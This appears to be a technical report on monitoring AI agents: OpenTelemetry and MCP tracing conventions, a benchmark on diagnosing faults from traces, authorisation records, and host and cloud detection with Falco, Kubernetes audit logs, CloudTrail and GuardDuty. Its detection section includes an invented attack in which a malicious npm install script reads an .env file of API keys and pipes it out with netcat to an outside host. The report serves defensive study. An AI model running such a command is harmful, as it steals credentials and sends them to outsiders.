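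`gen_ai.data_source.id` can also appear on an `invoke_agent` span, where it shows that the agent had a data source but not which step read from it or what that step read.

Ordinary database and web spans often have more detail because engineers designed their conventions for the services being called. The `SELECT customers` span exists because the MCP server's database library is instrumented. Without that instrumentation, the tree would end at the server's `tools/call` span, and an operator would know only that a tool called `query_customers` had run. The name does not show whether the tool only reads data, because its code might also allow an `UPDATE`.

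The database span still comes from the client's side, so it does not replace the database's own log.

### How trace context passes between programs

The harness, the MCP server and any other agents usually run as separate programs. Their spans form one tree only if each program passes trace context to the next. Trace context is mainly a string called `traceparent`, which has four parts separated by hyphens: a version number, the trace's identifier, the identifier of the calling span, and flags, one of which indicates whether the caller is recording the trace.

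Web services normally send this string as an HTTP header. MCP messages can also travel through the standard input and output of a local process, where there are no HTTP headers, so the string goes inside the message. Model Context Protocol puts it in a field called `_meta`. For the customer lookup, the message might be:

```json
{
  "jsonrpc": "2.0",
  "id": 2,
  "method": "tools/call",
  "params": {
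    "name": "query_customers",
    "arguments": {"customer_id": "C-2207"},
    "_meta": {
      "traceparent": "00-4bf92f3577b34da6a3ce929d0e0e4736-00f067aa0ba902b7-01"
    }
  }
}
```

The MCP client starts a span and writes the trace identifier and the span's identifier into its message to the server. The server reads both, starts its own span with the same trace identifier, and records the client's span as the parent. When the server then queries a database, the span for that query becomes a child of the server's span.

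Two optional fields can accompany `traceparent`. `tracestate` contains data for particular monitoring products, and `baggage` contains name-value pairs that the application chooses, such as a conversation identifier. Anything in `baggage` reaches the server's operator, so it is a poor place for personal data when another company runs the server.

Keys in `_meta` normally need a prefix based on a domain name. According to Model Context Protocol, the three trace-context keys are exempt because the C# SDK and other implementations already used them without a prefix. Arize's *Tracing For MCP Client Server Applications* (2025) announced one such implementation in April 2025. Another, a Go package documented in pkg.go.dev's *mcp* (2026), uses `_meta` to join client and server spans.

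Support for passing trace context can depend on a library's version. Strands Agents' *strands.tools.mcp.mcp_instrumentation* describes an agent-building kit whose client adds trace context to outgoing tool calls. The kit has to modify private parts of the official Python `mcp` package so that servers in the same process can read the context. It does this only for version 1, because version 2 passes trace context without help.

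#### When the context does not arrive

If the MCP server in the example ignored `traceparent`, the harness's trace would stop at the client's `tools/call` span. The server would start a second trace with a new identifier, and the `SELECT customers` span would be in that trace. Only the first trace would identify the agent and the conversation, so neither trace alone would link them to the query.

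An analyst could try to match the two traces by the tool's name and the time of the call, but this becomes guesswork if several agents call the same tool at once. The MCP session identifier would help if both the client and the server recorded it. According to an issue in FastMCP's repository, the framework set this identifier only on the server's span.

When another company runs a server, passing it the trace context does not give the operator that server's spans. The trace identifier would then be useful only for requesting the company's records.

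A harness can pass trace context to a shell command through an environment variable, a named value that a process receives when it starts. OpenTelemetry had not stabilised this method in 2026. The program would also need instrumentation to use the context, and most command-line programs have none.

Even an unbroken tree of spans can record failures incorrectly. According to the same FastMCP issue, the client's span was not marked as an error when a tool failed, because the framework raised the error after the span had ended. OpenObserve, a maker of monitoring software, points out that MCP also allows a server to report a failed tool call in a successful response containing the field `isError: true`. Instrumentation that ignores this field would leave the span's status unset.

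#### Between agents

Agents that delegate work to one another need to pass trace context too. *Autonomous Multi-modal Agents for ITOps Observability* (Siddharth, Garai and colleagues, 2026) describes an IBM system in which an orchestrator divides a request among five specialised agents. The agents communicate through Agent2Agent (A2A), a protocol that Google introduced in April 2025. The system uses OpenTelemetry to record model and tool calls, but each agent writes to its own log, so following a request requires joining the logs of all the agents it reached. According to the paper, passing trace context over A2A would make it possible to follow the request directly.

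In one of the paper's workflows, a user's question about costs goes from the orchestrator to all five other agents. The agent that generates database schemas is the only one of the six that doesn't load the recording software. Passing trace context would join the other five agents' logs, but the schema agent's model and tool calls would still be missing.

If that agent also failed to pass on the context it received, any agent it called would appear to have started a new, unrelated run. The records of the agents before and after it would then be disconnected, even if both agents had working instrumentation.

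According to OpenTelemetry, one proposal would add `gen_ai.workflow.name` to model-call, retrieval and tool spans, so that an analyst could still tell which pipeline a span came from if its parent were missing. The name is the same for every run of a pipeline, so the analyst would still have to work out which run the span belonged to.

### History and present status

OpenTelemetry set up a working group for generative AI in 2024, when each agent framework and monitoring product recorded model calls in its own way. OpenTelemetry's *AI Agent Observability* describes this fragmentation and presents common conventions as the solution.

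The conventions have changed a good deal since then. Version 1.37 replaced `gen_ai.system` with `gen_ai.provider.name`, and replaced separate events for individual messages with structured lists of messages. Later versions added retrieval spans, counts of cached tokens and the MCP conventions, which OpenTelemetry merged in January 2026. According to Greptime, version 1.41 added `invoke_workflow`, counts of reasoning tokens and metrics for streamed responses, and split `invoke_agent` in two.

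Upgrading a library does not necessarily change the attribute names it emits. OpenTelemetry's *Semantic conventions for generative AI systems* says that existing instrumentation based on version 1.36 or earlier should keep its old names by default. Operators can switch to the newer names by setting the environment variable `OTEL_SEMCONV_STABILITY_OPT_IN` to `gen_ai_latest_experimental`. Two agents in the same company may therefore both follow the conventions while one records `gen_ai.system` and the other `gen_ai.provider.name`. A search for only one of these attributes would miss the other agent.

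In 2026 OpenTelemetry moved its GenAI and MCP conventions from its main collection to a separate repository, which lets them change on their own schedule (Wang, 2026). The project created the repository on 5 May (OpenTelemetry, 2026), though Wang's *OpenTelemetry GenAI Conventions* dates the move to June. The project no longer maintains the old pages (OpenTelemetry, *Moved*).

#### Are the conventions stable?

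OpenTelemetry labels its conventions by maturity. "Development" means that names and structures may still change, while "Stable" promises that existing uses will keep working.

Secondary sources disagree about which stability label applies to the conventions. Business Tech Navigator reported in June 2026 that the GenAI group had released a stable specification in the new repository. In August, OpenObserve described the core attributes for model calls as stable or as release candidates, the stage before stability. Wang wrote the same month that the repository marked the conventions as Development and had no official release as of 21 August.

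OpenTelemetry's own pages support Wang. The last editions before the move and the edition that includes `invoke_workflow` mark the GenAI conventions as Development. In the April 2026 tables, the only attributes marked Stable are `error.type`, `server.address` and `server.port`, which OpenTelemetry uses for all kinds of software. Every attribute beginning with `gen_ai.` is marked Development. OpenTelemetry promised to update its transition instructions before declaring the conventions stable.

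The June report is hard to reconcile with this evidence, because the repository still had no releases in late August, and it would have had one if it had published a stable specification in June. The conventions were therefore still in Development in late August. The OpenTelemetry registry doesn't show whether this changed later, because in late November its stability column contained only a notice that each attribute had moved.

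Operators can use the conventions in the meantime if they check their alerts and saved searches after each upgrade. Greptime considers the core concepts settled, though the names may change. That seems reasonable for model calls and tool calls, which have kept the same basic meaning across recent versions. It is harder to judge for workflows, which OpenTelemetry added only in version 1.41.

### OpenInference and conformance checks

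OpenInference is another set of conventions for recording AI applications, with instrumentation libraries to go with it. It comes from Arize, a company that makes monitoring tools for AI. OpenInference uses OpenTelemetry's traces and export format, so its spans can go to the same storage, but it has its own attribute names:

| Information | OpenTelemetry GenAI | OpenInference |
|---|---|---|
| Kind of step | `gen_ai.operation.name`, such as `chat` | `openinference.span.kind`, such as `LLM` |
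| Model | `gen_ai.request.model` | `llm.model_name` |
| Input tokens | `gen_ai.usage.input_tokens` | `llm.token_count.prompt` |
| Tool | `gen_ai.tool.name` | `tool.name` |
| Conversation | `gen_ai.conversation.id` | `session.id` |
| User | No GenAI attribute | `user.id` |

The two also have different defaults for inputs and outputs. OpenInference's instrumentation records them unless the developer hides them, while OpenTelemetry's guidance is to leave them out unless the operator asks for them. An operator who switches from OpenInference to the GenAI conventions could therefore stop recording the text of prompts without meaning to.

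OpenInference also has an optional conversion, described in its *GenAI Conformance*, that adds `gen_ai.*` attributes alongside its own. Existing dashboards can then keep working while an operator moves to the newer names, but spans become larger.

According to the same document, OpenInference checks the result with Weaver, OpenTelemetry's tool for managing conventions. OpenTelemetry defines its attributes and spans in structured files and generates most of the human-readable pages from them. Weaver can compare these definitions with the telemetry a program emits.

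In OpenInference's test, the instrumentation calls mock model providers that return fixed responses, then exports the resulting traces to Weaver's `registry live-check` command. The test then prints a summary of which registry attributes appeared and which were missing. Because the responses are fixed, a developer can rerun the test after a change and be fairly confident that any difference came from the instrumentation.

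These checks are useful because instrumentation described as compatible may follow the conventions only partly. Some uses the correct attribute names but the wrong value types, and some uses the names without the structured message format. Separate implementations can also diverge. OpenTelemetry provides shared Python code for recording agents, tools and workflows, but a contributor pointed out that it had no equivalent for MCP, so the developers of each MCP library had to write their own. In one case, spans for listing an MCP server's tools appeared as "unknown".

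OpenTelemetry's new repository includes reference implementations and a table showing how well Python libraries follow the conventions. The project is also trying to reduce the work of supporting new frameworks. OpenTelemetry's *Building an Agent Harness for OTel Instrumentation with GenAI Semantic Conventions* (2026) describes an experiment in which a team of AI agents inspects a framework, proposes a plan and writes the instrumentation. The agents use Weaver to check the emitted telemetry, and engineers review the plan and the code.

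A successful check shows that the telemetry Weaver received matches the definitions, but the values may still be false. For example, if instrumentation records `openai` for a model that another company hosts, the value is still a valid provider name. Weaver also can't find a step that produced no telemetry. If the support agent's harness had no instrumentation for `send_email`, the remaining spans could all pass.

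## Is a trace that follows the conventions enough to explain what happened?

A trace that follows the conventions is usually not enough to explain what happened. The default attributes show which steps ran, in what order and for how long, but not the text that went into or came out of them. An operator can choose to record the text, but this reduces privacy and takes more storage. Even then, the conventions have no field for who authorised the agent to act.

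### Text that instrumentation leaves out by default

OpenTelemetry makes system instructions and tool definitions Opt-In, like messages, tool arguments and tool results. For the bulk deletion in the clean-up example, the missing text would have been useful in these ways:

| Attribute | What an investigator could learn from it |
|---|---|
| `gen_ai.system_instructions` | Whether the operator's standing instructions ruled out bulk deletion |
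| `gen_ai.input.messages` | The phrase "clean up old records", and whatever else the agent had read |
| `gen_ai.output.messages` | The call the model requested, and any text it wrote first |
| `gen_ai.tool.definitions` | Whether the description of `delete_records` explained the wildcard |
| `gen_ai.tool.call.arguments` | The wildcard itself |
| `gen_ai.tool.call.result` | The number of deleted rows, if the tool returned it |

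These attributes overlap because a model's output contains the arguments of every tool call it requests, and the next prompt normally contains the result. An operator who chooses to record messages but not tool arguments, perhaps to protect customer data, will probably store the arguments anyway.

In April 2026 OpenTelemetry advised against recording tool definitions by default because they can be large, but it later narrowed this advice to the optional parts of a definition.

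Claude Code's events also omit this text by default. According to Niemi, an operator can include prompts by setting `OTEL_LOG_USER_PROMPTS=1` and tool arguments by setting `OTEL_LOG_TOOL_DETAILS=1`. Someone investigating the clean-up would need both.

### Why the text is off by default

OpenTelemetry's reasons are that the text is often sensitive and large. Storing it can be expensive or conflict with regulations, and a company may want to give different people access to operational data and user data. For example, an engineer who only needs to know why an agent is slow should not necessarily be able to read customers' messages.

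Traces can also expose secrets. If an agent opens a configuration file that contains a password, the password becomes part of the next prompt, and a trace with full messages will contain it too. *Observability in Agentic Networking*, a proposal from the Kubernetes project Kube Agentic Networking for tracing agents' traffic through gateways, includes a similar case. An agent tries to send an email with a social security number and a card number in the body, and the gateway blocks it. If the trace included the tool's arguments, both numbers would be stored even though the email was never sent. The proposal's example instead records the kinds of data the gateway found and the field that contained them.

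Storage costs grow quickly if every model-call span includes its full input, because harnesses such as Codex send the whole conversation with every call. If each call adds 2,000 tokens to the conversation and a turn has 100 calls, the conversation ends up 200,000 tokens long. The trace, however, contains 2,000 × (1 + 2 + … + 100) tokens, which is about 10 million, or 50 times as much.

### Redaction, separate storage and filtering

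OpenTelemetry describes two ways to record instructions, inputs and outputs. An operator can put them on the spans, which OpenTelemetry considers best when volumes are manageable and either no privacy rules apply or the storage meets them, as in testing before release. For production systems with large volumes or sensitive data, it recommends storing the text elsewhere, where it can have its own access rules, and putting a reference to it on the span.

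To support separate storage, instrumentation can let the operator supply a function, called a hook. The instrumentation passes the text and the span to the hook, which can redact the text before saving it. OpenTelemetry has not yet settled on a common format for the references, so one vendor's tool may not be able to follow references written by another's.

Redaction works best when it replaces specific values, such as a card number in an email, with labels, so that investigators can still read the rest. Another option is to store a hash, a short fingerprint calculated from the text. Kube Agentic Networking suggests this for prompts when an agent retries a step. An analyst can compare hashes to check whether two prompts were identical, but can't recover the wording from them.

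OpenTelemetry allows instrumentation to shorten long messages, and a storage system may limit their size even if the instrumentation doesn't. This truncation may remove an injected instruction halfway through a long web page, although a wildcard is short enough to be kept.

Many operators also send telemetry through the OpenTelemetry Collector, a program that can edit, drop or redirect it before storage. CNCF's *Filtering and reducing AI agent telemetry with the OpenTelemetry Collector* (2026) describes a coding agent's telemetry as expensive to store and hard to make sense of. Niemi's team uses a Collector to send events from Claude Code and Cowork to separate data sets.

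A Collector can remove a password before anyone stores it, but by then the password has already left the agent's machine. Filters can also remove evidence. For example, dropping every successful tool call would save a lot of space but delete the only span that recorded the bulk deletion.

### What sampling does to a rare event

Sampling means keeping some traces and discarding the rest. In head sampling, the program decides whether to keep a trace when the trace begins, before the agent has chosen any action, so the decision can't depend on what the agent does.

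Suppose an agent handles 100,000 requests a day and the operator keeps a random 1% of the traces. Those 1,000 traces are enough to measure common problems. If 5% of requests fail, the sample will contain about 50 failures, and the estimated failure rate will usually be within 1.4 percentage points of the true rate.

A single bulk deletion has a 1% chance of being in the sample. If the same mistake happens in *n* separate traces, the chance of keeping at least one of them is 1 − 0.99ⁿ:

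| Traces with the mistake | Chance of keeping at least one |
|---|---|
| 1 | 1% |
| 10 | 9.6% |
| 100 | 63.4% |
| 299 | 95.0% |

An incident that spans two traces is even less likely to be kept in full. If an agent reads an injected instruction in one turn and acts on it in the next, each turn may have its own trace. If each trace is sampled independently at 1%, the chance of keeping both is 1 in 10,000.

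In tail sampling, the operator's software waits until a trace is complete before deciding whether to keep it. It can then keep every trace that contains an error and 1% of the others. The bulk deletion produced no error, so its trace still has only a 1% chance of being kept. A rule that keeps every trace containing `delete_records` would catch it, but only if someone had thought of that tool in advance.

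OpenTelemetry's hook partly avoids this problem because instrumentation should call it whether or not the sampler keeps the span. An operator could therefore save the text of every model call while keeping only 1% of spans. The hook would need to save the trace's identifier with the text, because any reference stored on a span is lost when the span is discarded.

### Finding a failure and finding its origin

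In *TelemetrySuffBench*, Zhu and Pu (2026) tested how much an investigator loses when a trace lacks this text. They gave traces to five language models and asked them whether each run had gone wrong and, if so, at which step the fault began.

The benchmark has 312 generated traces. In each, a pipeline of agent components has to update a particular record (a ticket, document or order) and check the result. Ninety-six of the runs are clean. In the other 216, Zhu and Pu made one component choose a valid reference to the wrong record. Nothing fails until several steps later, when another component looks up the reference, the update succeeds on the wrong record, and a final check finds the mismatch. The faulty runs come in pairs with the same task and ending but different origins of the error, so the origin can't be identified from the ending alone.

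Zhu and Pu then produced six versions of every trace, so that differences in the scores would come from what the models could read and not from the runs themselves. Detection is measured by F1, which is 100% only if a model misses no faulty run and raises no false alarm. The ranges cover all five models:

| Version of the trace | What it contains | Detection F1 | Origin step found |
|---|---|---|---|
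| Full | Everything except the answers | 99.3–100% | 33.8–97.2% |
| OpenTelemetry-compatible | Identity, tool, observation, status and links between steps | 99.5–100% | At most 0.5% |
| OpenInference-compatible | The same fields | 99.5–100% | At most 0.5% |
| Metadata | Identity, status, links, tool names and tool arguments | 99.5–100% | At most 0.5% |
| Content-redacted | Steps, statuses and links, with the text blanked out | 78.9–100% | At most 0.5% |
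| Structural | Only the order, type, status and links of the steps | 82.7–100% | 0% |

With the OpenTelemetry-compatible version, the models could tell that a run had failed but almost never where the failure began. In 99% of cases, they blamed the update to the wrong record, which was a symptom of an earlier bad choice. The metadata version included tool arguments but did no better, because it left out the text of that choice.

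#### Which details mattered

In a second experiment, Zhu and Pu removed one kind of information at a time from the full traces. Without the text of the component's choice, no model found any origin. This result is partly due to the design. Removing the choice makes the two traces in a pair identical, so a model that answers consistently can be right about at most one of them. The models did not reach even that limit, because 98.1% of their answers named the later step that looked up the reference.

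Removing both the retrieved documents and the list that linked references to records cut accuracy to between 9% and 66%. With tool inputs and changes of state removed instead, accuracy stayed between 81.2% and 100%, and four of the five models did at least as well as with the full trace. An operator who can't store everything might therefore do better to keep what the agent chose and the material it chose from than to keep every tool's output. This lesson is tentative because it depends on how these particular faults work.

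#### Asking a model to explain an incomplete trace

Zhu and Pu also gave the models pairs of traces that looked exactly the same but had different origins. The only correct answer was that the evidence was insufficient, and the prompt told the models to give that answer when it applied. When the traces contained very little, every model did so. When they contained a lot of detail, several models named an origin anyway. A stricter prompt, which told them to rule out the alternatives first, helped three of the five:

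| Model | Origin found in full traces | Unsupported answers, basic prompt | Unsupported answers, stricter prompt |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 5 | 97.2% | 12.5% | 0% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 97.2% | 44.4% | 13.9% |
| GPT-5.5 | 90.3% | 87.5% | 38.9% |
| DeepSeek-V4-Pro | 84.7% | 100% | 100% |
| Qwen 3.7 Max | 33.8% | 100% | 100% |

The stricter prompt also made some models too cautious. GPT-5.6 Sol declined to answer 34% of the answerable detailed cases, up from 24.3%. GPT-5.5 is perhaps more worrying for an operator. It found nine in ten origins when the evidence was present, but under the basic prompt it also usually named an origin when the evidence was missing.

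#### How far the results apply

The faults are artificial, and nearly all of them work the same way. Zhu and Pu repeated the main comparison with new traces from the same generator and got similar results. They also tried a second kind of fault, in which a component accepts evidence it should have questioned. GPT-5.6 Sol found the origin of 92% of these faults with full traces and none without the text of the decision, but this test used only 25 faulty runs and one model.

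The OpenTelemetry-compatible version is also a conservative reading of the conventions, with only generic fields. Zhu and Pu used the same fields for OpenInference, although its instrumentation records inputs and outputs by default. The 0.5% figure is therefore evidence about sparse traces. An operator who turns on `gen_ai.output.messages` could record the choice that this version leaves out, but the benchmark does not measure how well a model would do with such a trace.

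The detection scores need more caution because every faulty run ends with a check that already has the right answer, compares it with the changed record and logs a failure. The harmful step itself, the update to the wrong record, succeeds. Production systems often have no such check, and the bulk deletion had none. Its trace would end like that of a clean run, so a detection score near 100% is no reason to expect a model to notice the deletion.

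A model might still notice a harmful success from the text alone. The models found many origins when Zhu and Pu removed either the final check's comparison or the failure status. But the experiment never removed both together, so it doesn't show how the models would do with no sign of failure.

### Complete traces of real failures

TraceElephant, a benchmark by Chen and colleagues, uses failures that agent systems produced on their own. It compares complete traces with partial ones that contain the agents' outputs but not their inputs or the surrounding context. According to Zhu and Pu, complete traces improved the attribution of failures by up to 76.5%, though the typical gain may be much smaller. This is still a reason to record agents' inputs and context as well as their outputs.

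Zhu and Pu ran their five models on 218 TraceElephant traces from the agent systems Captain-Agent, Magentic-One and SWE-Agent. With the full text, the models identified the decisive step in 9.6% to 24.3% of cases and the responsible component in 16.1% to 41.7%. With the text blanked out, both figures were zero for every model.

The text was therefore necessary here too, but far from enough. The best model missed the decisive step in about three-quarters of these failures, while two models found 97.2% of the origins in the artificial traces. Some of the difference may arise because Zhu and Pu cut the middle out of any request longer than 3,000 characters. Real failures are probably also harder to diagnose, since they don't follow one pattern and may have several contributing causes. All 218 runs had failed, so this test also doesn't show whether models can recognise harm in a run that appears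 to have succeeded.

### Who authorised the action

Full text would show the operations team's instruction in the clean-up example, but not necessarily whether the person who typed it had the authority to order a deletion, what limits applied, or whether anyone approved the call. The company TinyFish argues that the conventions suit a developer looking for a bug better than an auditor, who needs to know who authorised the agent, under what constraints, and whether it kept to them.

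OpenTelemetry's list of GenAI attributes supports this criticism. In late November 2026 it had no attribute for delegation, permission, policy or approval. The closest are the `gen_ai.evaluation.*` attributes, which contain a score, a label such as "pass" and an explanation. A team could use them to record a policy check, but OpenTelemetry intends them for judging a model's response, and they have no field for the approver's name or the approved call. Claude Code's `tool_decision` event records some of this, in Anthropic's own format.

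#### Proposals for permission checks

Kube Agentic Networking proposes standard fields for the gateway's decision. `event.action` is `allow` or `deny`, and `event.outcome` records whether the check worked, so if the check works and the gateway refuses a request, the values are `deny` and `success`. Another span records the rule behind the decision. Under the proposal, programs also use `baggage` to pass each other the identifier of the user who delegated authority.

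In one of its examples, an agent calls `delete_customer_data` and the gateway refuses because the user's role doesn't allow deletion. The gateway's span has the HTTP status 403 and an error, but the agent's own span for the same tool call has the status OK. An analyst with only the agent's spans could easily conclude that the deletion went through.

*OTEP*, a May 2026 proposal by the GitHub contributor eeee2345, suggested five attributes for recording the results of threat detection, including the rule that matched, its severity and the action taken. The action could be `allow`, `block`, `warn` or `ask`, where `ask` sends the case to a person for approval. None of the five attributes records who that person was or what they answered. Nobody rejected the idea itself, but the contributor closed the proposal the same day, after a maintainer explained that this kind of work belonged in a different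 repository.

Another proposal on GitHub would add an event for an action that a system considered but deliberately did not take. At present, a trace in which a policy stopped the agent from taking an action may look the same as one in which the agent never considered it.

Some vendors have defined their own fields without a standard. Microsoft's *Interface GuardrailFinding* documents fields in the company's OpenTelemetry package for the policy that triggered a finding, the policy's version and the decision. Recording the version helps investigators because the policy may have changed since the incident.

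#### Limits and delegation

Proposals for recording the limits on a task are further from OpenTelemetry. *Agent Operation Authorization* (2026) is an Internet-Draft from the Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), which means it is a working document and not a standard. It describes a token, a digital credential that a server issues after the user agrees to an operation. The token identifies the agent and records the user's confirmation, and the draft expresses the proposed operation as a policy that software can check.

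This would answer more of an auditor's questions than an `allow` or `deny` field, but the answers would be in the token, not in the trace. To connect the two, spans would need to include some identifier for the token. Copying the token itself into the trace would be dangerous, because anyone who could read the trace might then be able to use the token.

An agent identifier on every span would show which agents took part in a task, but not whether one of them exceeded the authority delegated to it. When agents pass parts of a task down a chain, each should receive no more authority than the one before. According to IETF's *Cross-Org Agent Delegation* (2026), another Internet-Draft, existing tokens typically have a fixed set of permissions and no built-in way for an outside organisation to verify that each step only narrowed them.

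Even a complete record of permissions might not reveal the mistake in the clean-up. The agent's account was allowed to delete records, so a permission check would probably have returned `allow`. To show that the agent broke a limit, the record would need to include the limit, such as "only records from before 2015", and someone would have had to write that down before the agent started.

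## What do tools that detect host and control-plane compromise look for?

Tools that detect compromise look for activity that matches a known attack technique or departs from what a machine or account normally does. Their evidence comes mainly from the operating system and cloud audit logs, so it can exist even when an agent's harness has no instrumentation.

### From system events to an alert

A program needs the operating system's kernel for almost anything that reaches beyond its own memory. On Linux, it makes system calls, such as `execve` to start another program, `openat` to open a file and `connect` to reach another machine. Detection software records these calls and the process that made each one. On Windows, Microsoft's Sysmon records similar events, including new processes, network connections and, if an administrator enables this, lookups of server names (Canale and Soulis, 2026,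 *Detecting Shadow AI*).

Suppose an agent in a container installs an MCP server from npm, the public registry of JavaScript packages, and the package is malicious. In this invented example, process 300 is the harness:

| Event | Process | Parent | Detail |
|---|---|---|---|
| Program starts | 412 | 300 | `bash -c "npm install example-mcp"` |
| Program starts | 413 | 412 | `npm install example-mcp` |
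| Program starts | 420 | 413 | `sh setup.sh`, a script from the package |
| File opens | 420 | 413 | `/app/.env`, which contains the agent's API keys |
| Program starts | 421 | 420 | `nc files.example.net 4444` |
| Connection opens | 421 | 420 | `files.example.net`, port 4444 |

The software builds a process tree by matching each process's parent number to an earlier process. The last row alone shows only that `nc` (netcat, a program for sending data over a network) contacted an unfamiliar server. The tree links `nc` to a package installation that the agent started. A tree can have gaps, because a parent may exit before its child, and operating systems reuse process numbers.

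A detection rule is a condition that the software tests against each event. Falco and Aqua Security's Tracee are open-source tools that detect suspicious system calls on Linux. One rule in Falco's *Default Rules* matches the start of `nc` in this example. It triggers an alert when a network tool starts in a container, one of the tool's ancestor processes is an npm installation, and the operator has not listed the activity as expected. The alert includes the command and four generations of ancestors. If the package had sent the file from its own JavaScript code, no network tool would have started and the rule would have missed the transfer. The rule also doesn't apply to a coding agent that runs on a developer's laptop outside a container.

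A behavioural model compares new events with the past activity of the same user, machine or program, rather than with a written condition, and raises an alert when the difference is large enough. EDR products also have rules for behaviour that is suspicious almost anywhere. Canale and Soulis give the examples of a document editor starting a shell and a process injecting code into another process.

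### One Falco rule, part by part

Falco's rule "Terminal shell in container" has a condition with six parts, all of which must be true. iximiuz Labs' *Lesson in Kubelings*, a Kubernetes course, defines several of them in a simplified version of the rule:

| Part of the condition | Meaning |
|---|---|
| `spawned_process` | A program has just started through `execve` or the related call `execveat` |
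| `container` | The program is in a container, not directly on the host |
| `shell_procs` | The program is a shell, such as `bash`, `sh` or `zsh` |
| `proc.tty != 0` | The shell has a terminal attached, as it would if a person were typing |
| `container_entrypoint` | The shell is the way into the container, so its parent is the software that runs containers or has already exited |
| `not user_expected_terminal_shell_in_container_conditions` | The operator has not listed this case as expected |

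Falco raises this alert when an intruder opens an interactive shell in a container, but also when an engineer opens one with the ordinary Kubernetes command `kubectl exec` to investigate a fault. Falco gives the alert the low priority "notice" and suggests using it as an audit record when examining other alerts from the same container.

The agent's own shell commands usually would not meet the condition, because when a harness runs `bash -c "cat README.md"`, the shell's parent is the harness and there is often no terminal. The rule could still fire if the harness sent its commands into a separate sandbox container through an interactive session.

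A broader rule, "Shell spawned by untrusted binary", detects shells started by applications on a list the operator can edit. Falco recommends it for detecting remote code execution, in which an outsider exploits a flaw to run commands on the machine. The rule's condition has 20 exceptions, mostly for ordinary software that starts shells as part of its work.

How useful this rule is for an agent depends on the agent's tools. Suppose a flaw in an agent framework lets an outsider run commands inside the agent's process. A support assistant that only calls web services has no reason to start a shell, so a shell is strong evidence of an attack. But a coding agent may start hundreds of shells a day, and an operator who put its harness on the list would get an alert for every one.

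In July 2025, only 25 of Falco's 90 rules were in its default release package. The default set doesn't include the npm rule or a rule for containers that contact the cloud provider's metadata service, from which programs can obtain credentials. Rules for connections to unapproved destinations are disabled by default because operators first have to work out which destinations their software normally uses. That list may be impossible to write for an agent that browses the web.

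### What Kubernetes records at each level

An intruder may not need a shell if they can give orders to the control plane. Kubernetes receives those orders through its API, and its audit policy sets one of four levels for each kind of request:

| Level | What the log contains |
|---|---|
| `None` | Nothing |
| `Metadata` | Who made the request, when, on which resource and with which operation |
| `Request` | The same, plus the body of the request |
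| `RequestResponse` | The same, plus the body of the response |

For example, an intruder might create a container that can read the host's entire disk. At `Metadata`, the log would contain the container's name and the account that created it. The setting that exposed the disk is in the request body, so an investigator would need `Request` to find it. Higher levels can also expose secrets, because `RequestResponse` copies a stored password into the log if someone reads it through the API.

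When someone runs `kubectl exec`, the audit log identifies the account that requested the shell but not the commands typed into it. Falco can record the programs those commands start but may not identify the person. The Falco project recommends combining the two records by matching the container's name and location in the cluster. The match is approximate because two people may have shells open in the same container.

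Kubernetes can log both reads and changes made through its API. An agent's query to a database running on Kubernetes goes directly to the database, so the Kubernetes audit log doesn't record it.

### Which cloud operations leave a record by default

By default, CloudTrail logs control-plane operations, which AWS calls management events, but not data events such as the DynamoDB deletions in the clean-up example. AWS lists two other event categories, for requests over private network connections and for unusual rates of calls or errors.

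According to AWS's *Working with CloudTrail event history*, customers can search the past 90 days of management events in each Region, AWS's term for a geographic group of data centres. To log data events, customers must configure a trail or an event data store and explicitly add each type of resource, according to AWS's *Logging data events*. AWS charges extra for data events.

| Operation | Category | Logged by default? |
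|---|---|---|
| Create a storage bucket | Management | Yes |
| Change who may use the bucket | Management | Yes |
| Retrieve a password from AWS's secrets service | Management | Yes, with a caveat |
| Read a file in the bucket | Data | No |
| Delete an item from a DynamoDB table | Data | No |
| Search a knowledge base in Bedrock, AWS's service for models and agents | Data | No |

AWS says the default history covers events that create, modify or delete resources, and tells customers to configure a trail for a complete record that includes read-only activity. An operator who may need to prove who retrieved a password should not rely on the default history, because retrieving a password is a read-only operation.

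If an intruder uses a stolen key to copy every customer file from a bucket, the default log may show the intruder exploring the account but not the copying, because it omits data events. The same gap makes it harder to find out whether an agent read files it should not have. Turning on data events afterwards records only later reads.

AWS also treats much of the activity in its own agent services as data events. These include activity on Bedrock agents, prompts and guardrails (filters on a model's inputs and outputs), and on the gateway, memory and code interpreter of AgentCore, AWS's platform for running agents. An audit log that runs throughout an incident can therefore contain few of the agent's actions.

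### How a stolen cloud credential gives itself away

GuardDuty, AWS's threat-detection service, analyses CloudTrail events and other records and reports suspicious activity as "findings". One finding concerns the temporary credentials that programs on a virtual machine use to call AWS. These credentials let an agent on the machine call AWS without storing a password, but a malicious package on the same machine may be able to steal them.

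If the thief uses the credentials on a laptop, AWS accepts the requests because the credentials are valid. But the source address doesn't match the machine the credentials came from, so GuardDuty reports `InstanceCredentialExfiltration.OutsideAWS`. According to AWS, this finding means that an outside host tried to use credentials created on one of the customer's virtual machines. The customer can suppress the finding if the address belongs to them or someone they trust.

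A thief could once avoid this finding by using the credentials on a machine rented from AWS. In January 2022, AWS (2022) added a second finding for credentials used from an address that belongs to another AWS account. As AWS describes them, neither finding would cover an intruder who sends requests from the original machine, because the address is correct.

Other findings rely on a behavioural model. According to AWS's *GuardDuty IAM finding types*, the model evaluates every API request in an account and tracks factors such as the user, the location and the operation. All three matter if, for example, an agent's account that has only ever listed virtual machines creates a new access key from another country. The finding's details show which factors were unusual for that account.

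GuardDuty groups these anomalies by their likely purpose. For example, unusual requests for passwords fall under credential access, and new access keys fall under persistence, an intruder's attempt to keep access. Its anomaly finding for exfiltration, the removal of data, covers only control-plane operations such as copying a whole database, so it would not cover reading the files in a bucket one by one.

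Two GuardDuty findings do not depend on unusual behaviour by the account. GuardDuty reports when someone uses a key that Amazon's threat intelligence has identified as potentially compromised, and when someone turns off the logging of model calls in Bedrock. AWS treats turning off this logging as a possible attempt to hide data theft or model misuse. An operator whose only copy of an agent's prompts is in that log would want to know quickly.

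GuardDuty's credential findings cover access to AWS. If someone steals the API key a harness uses to call OpenAI or Anthropic directly, the thief's requests go to that provider and never appear in CloudTrail. The operator would have to look for them in the provider's usage records or bills.

### The agent platform's own control plane

An intruder can also take control of an agent by changing its configuration, without running a malicious program or stealing data directly. A new system prompt changes the agent's standing instructions, a wider permission removes a check on its tool calls, and a new MCP server gives it tools that someone else controls. Whether the change leaves a record depends on where the configuration is:

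| Change | Where someone makes it | Likely record |
|---|---|---|
| Instructions of an agent on a hosted platform | The platform's console or API | The platform's audit log |
| System prompt in an application's source code | The code repository | The repository's history |
| Commands a coding agent may run without asking | A settings file on the developer's machine | None, unless host software records changes to the file |
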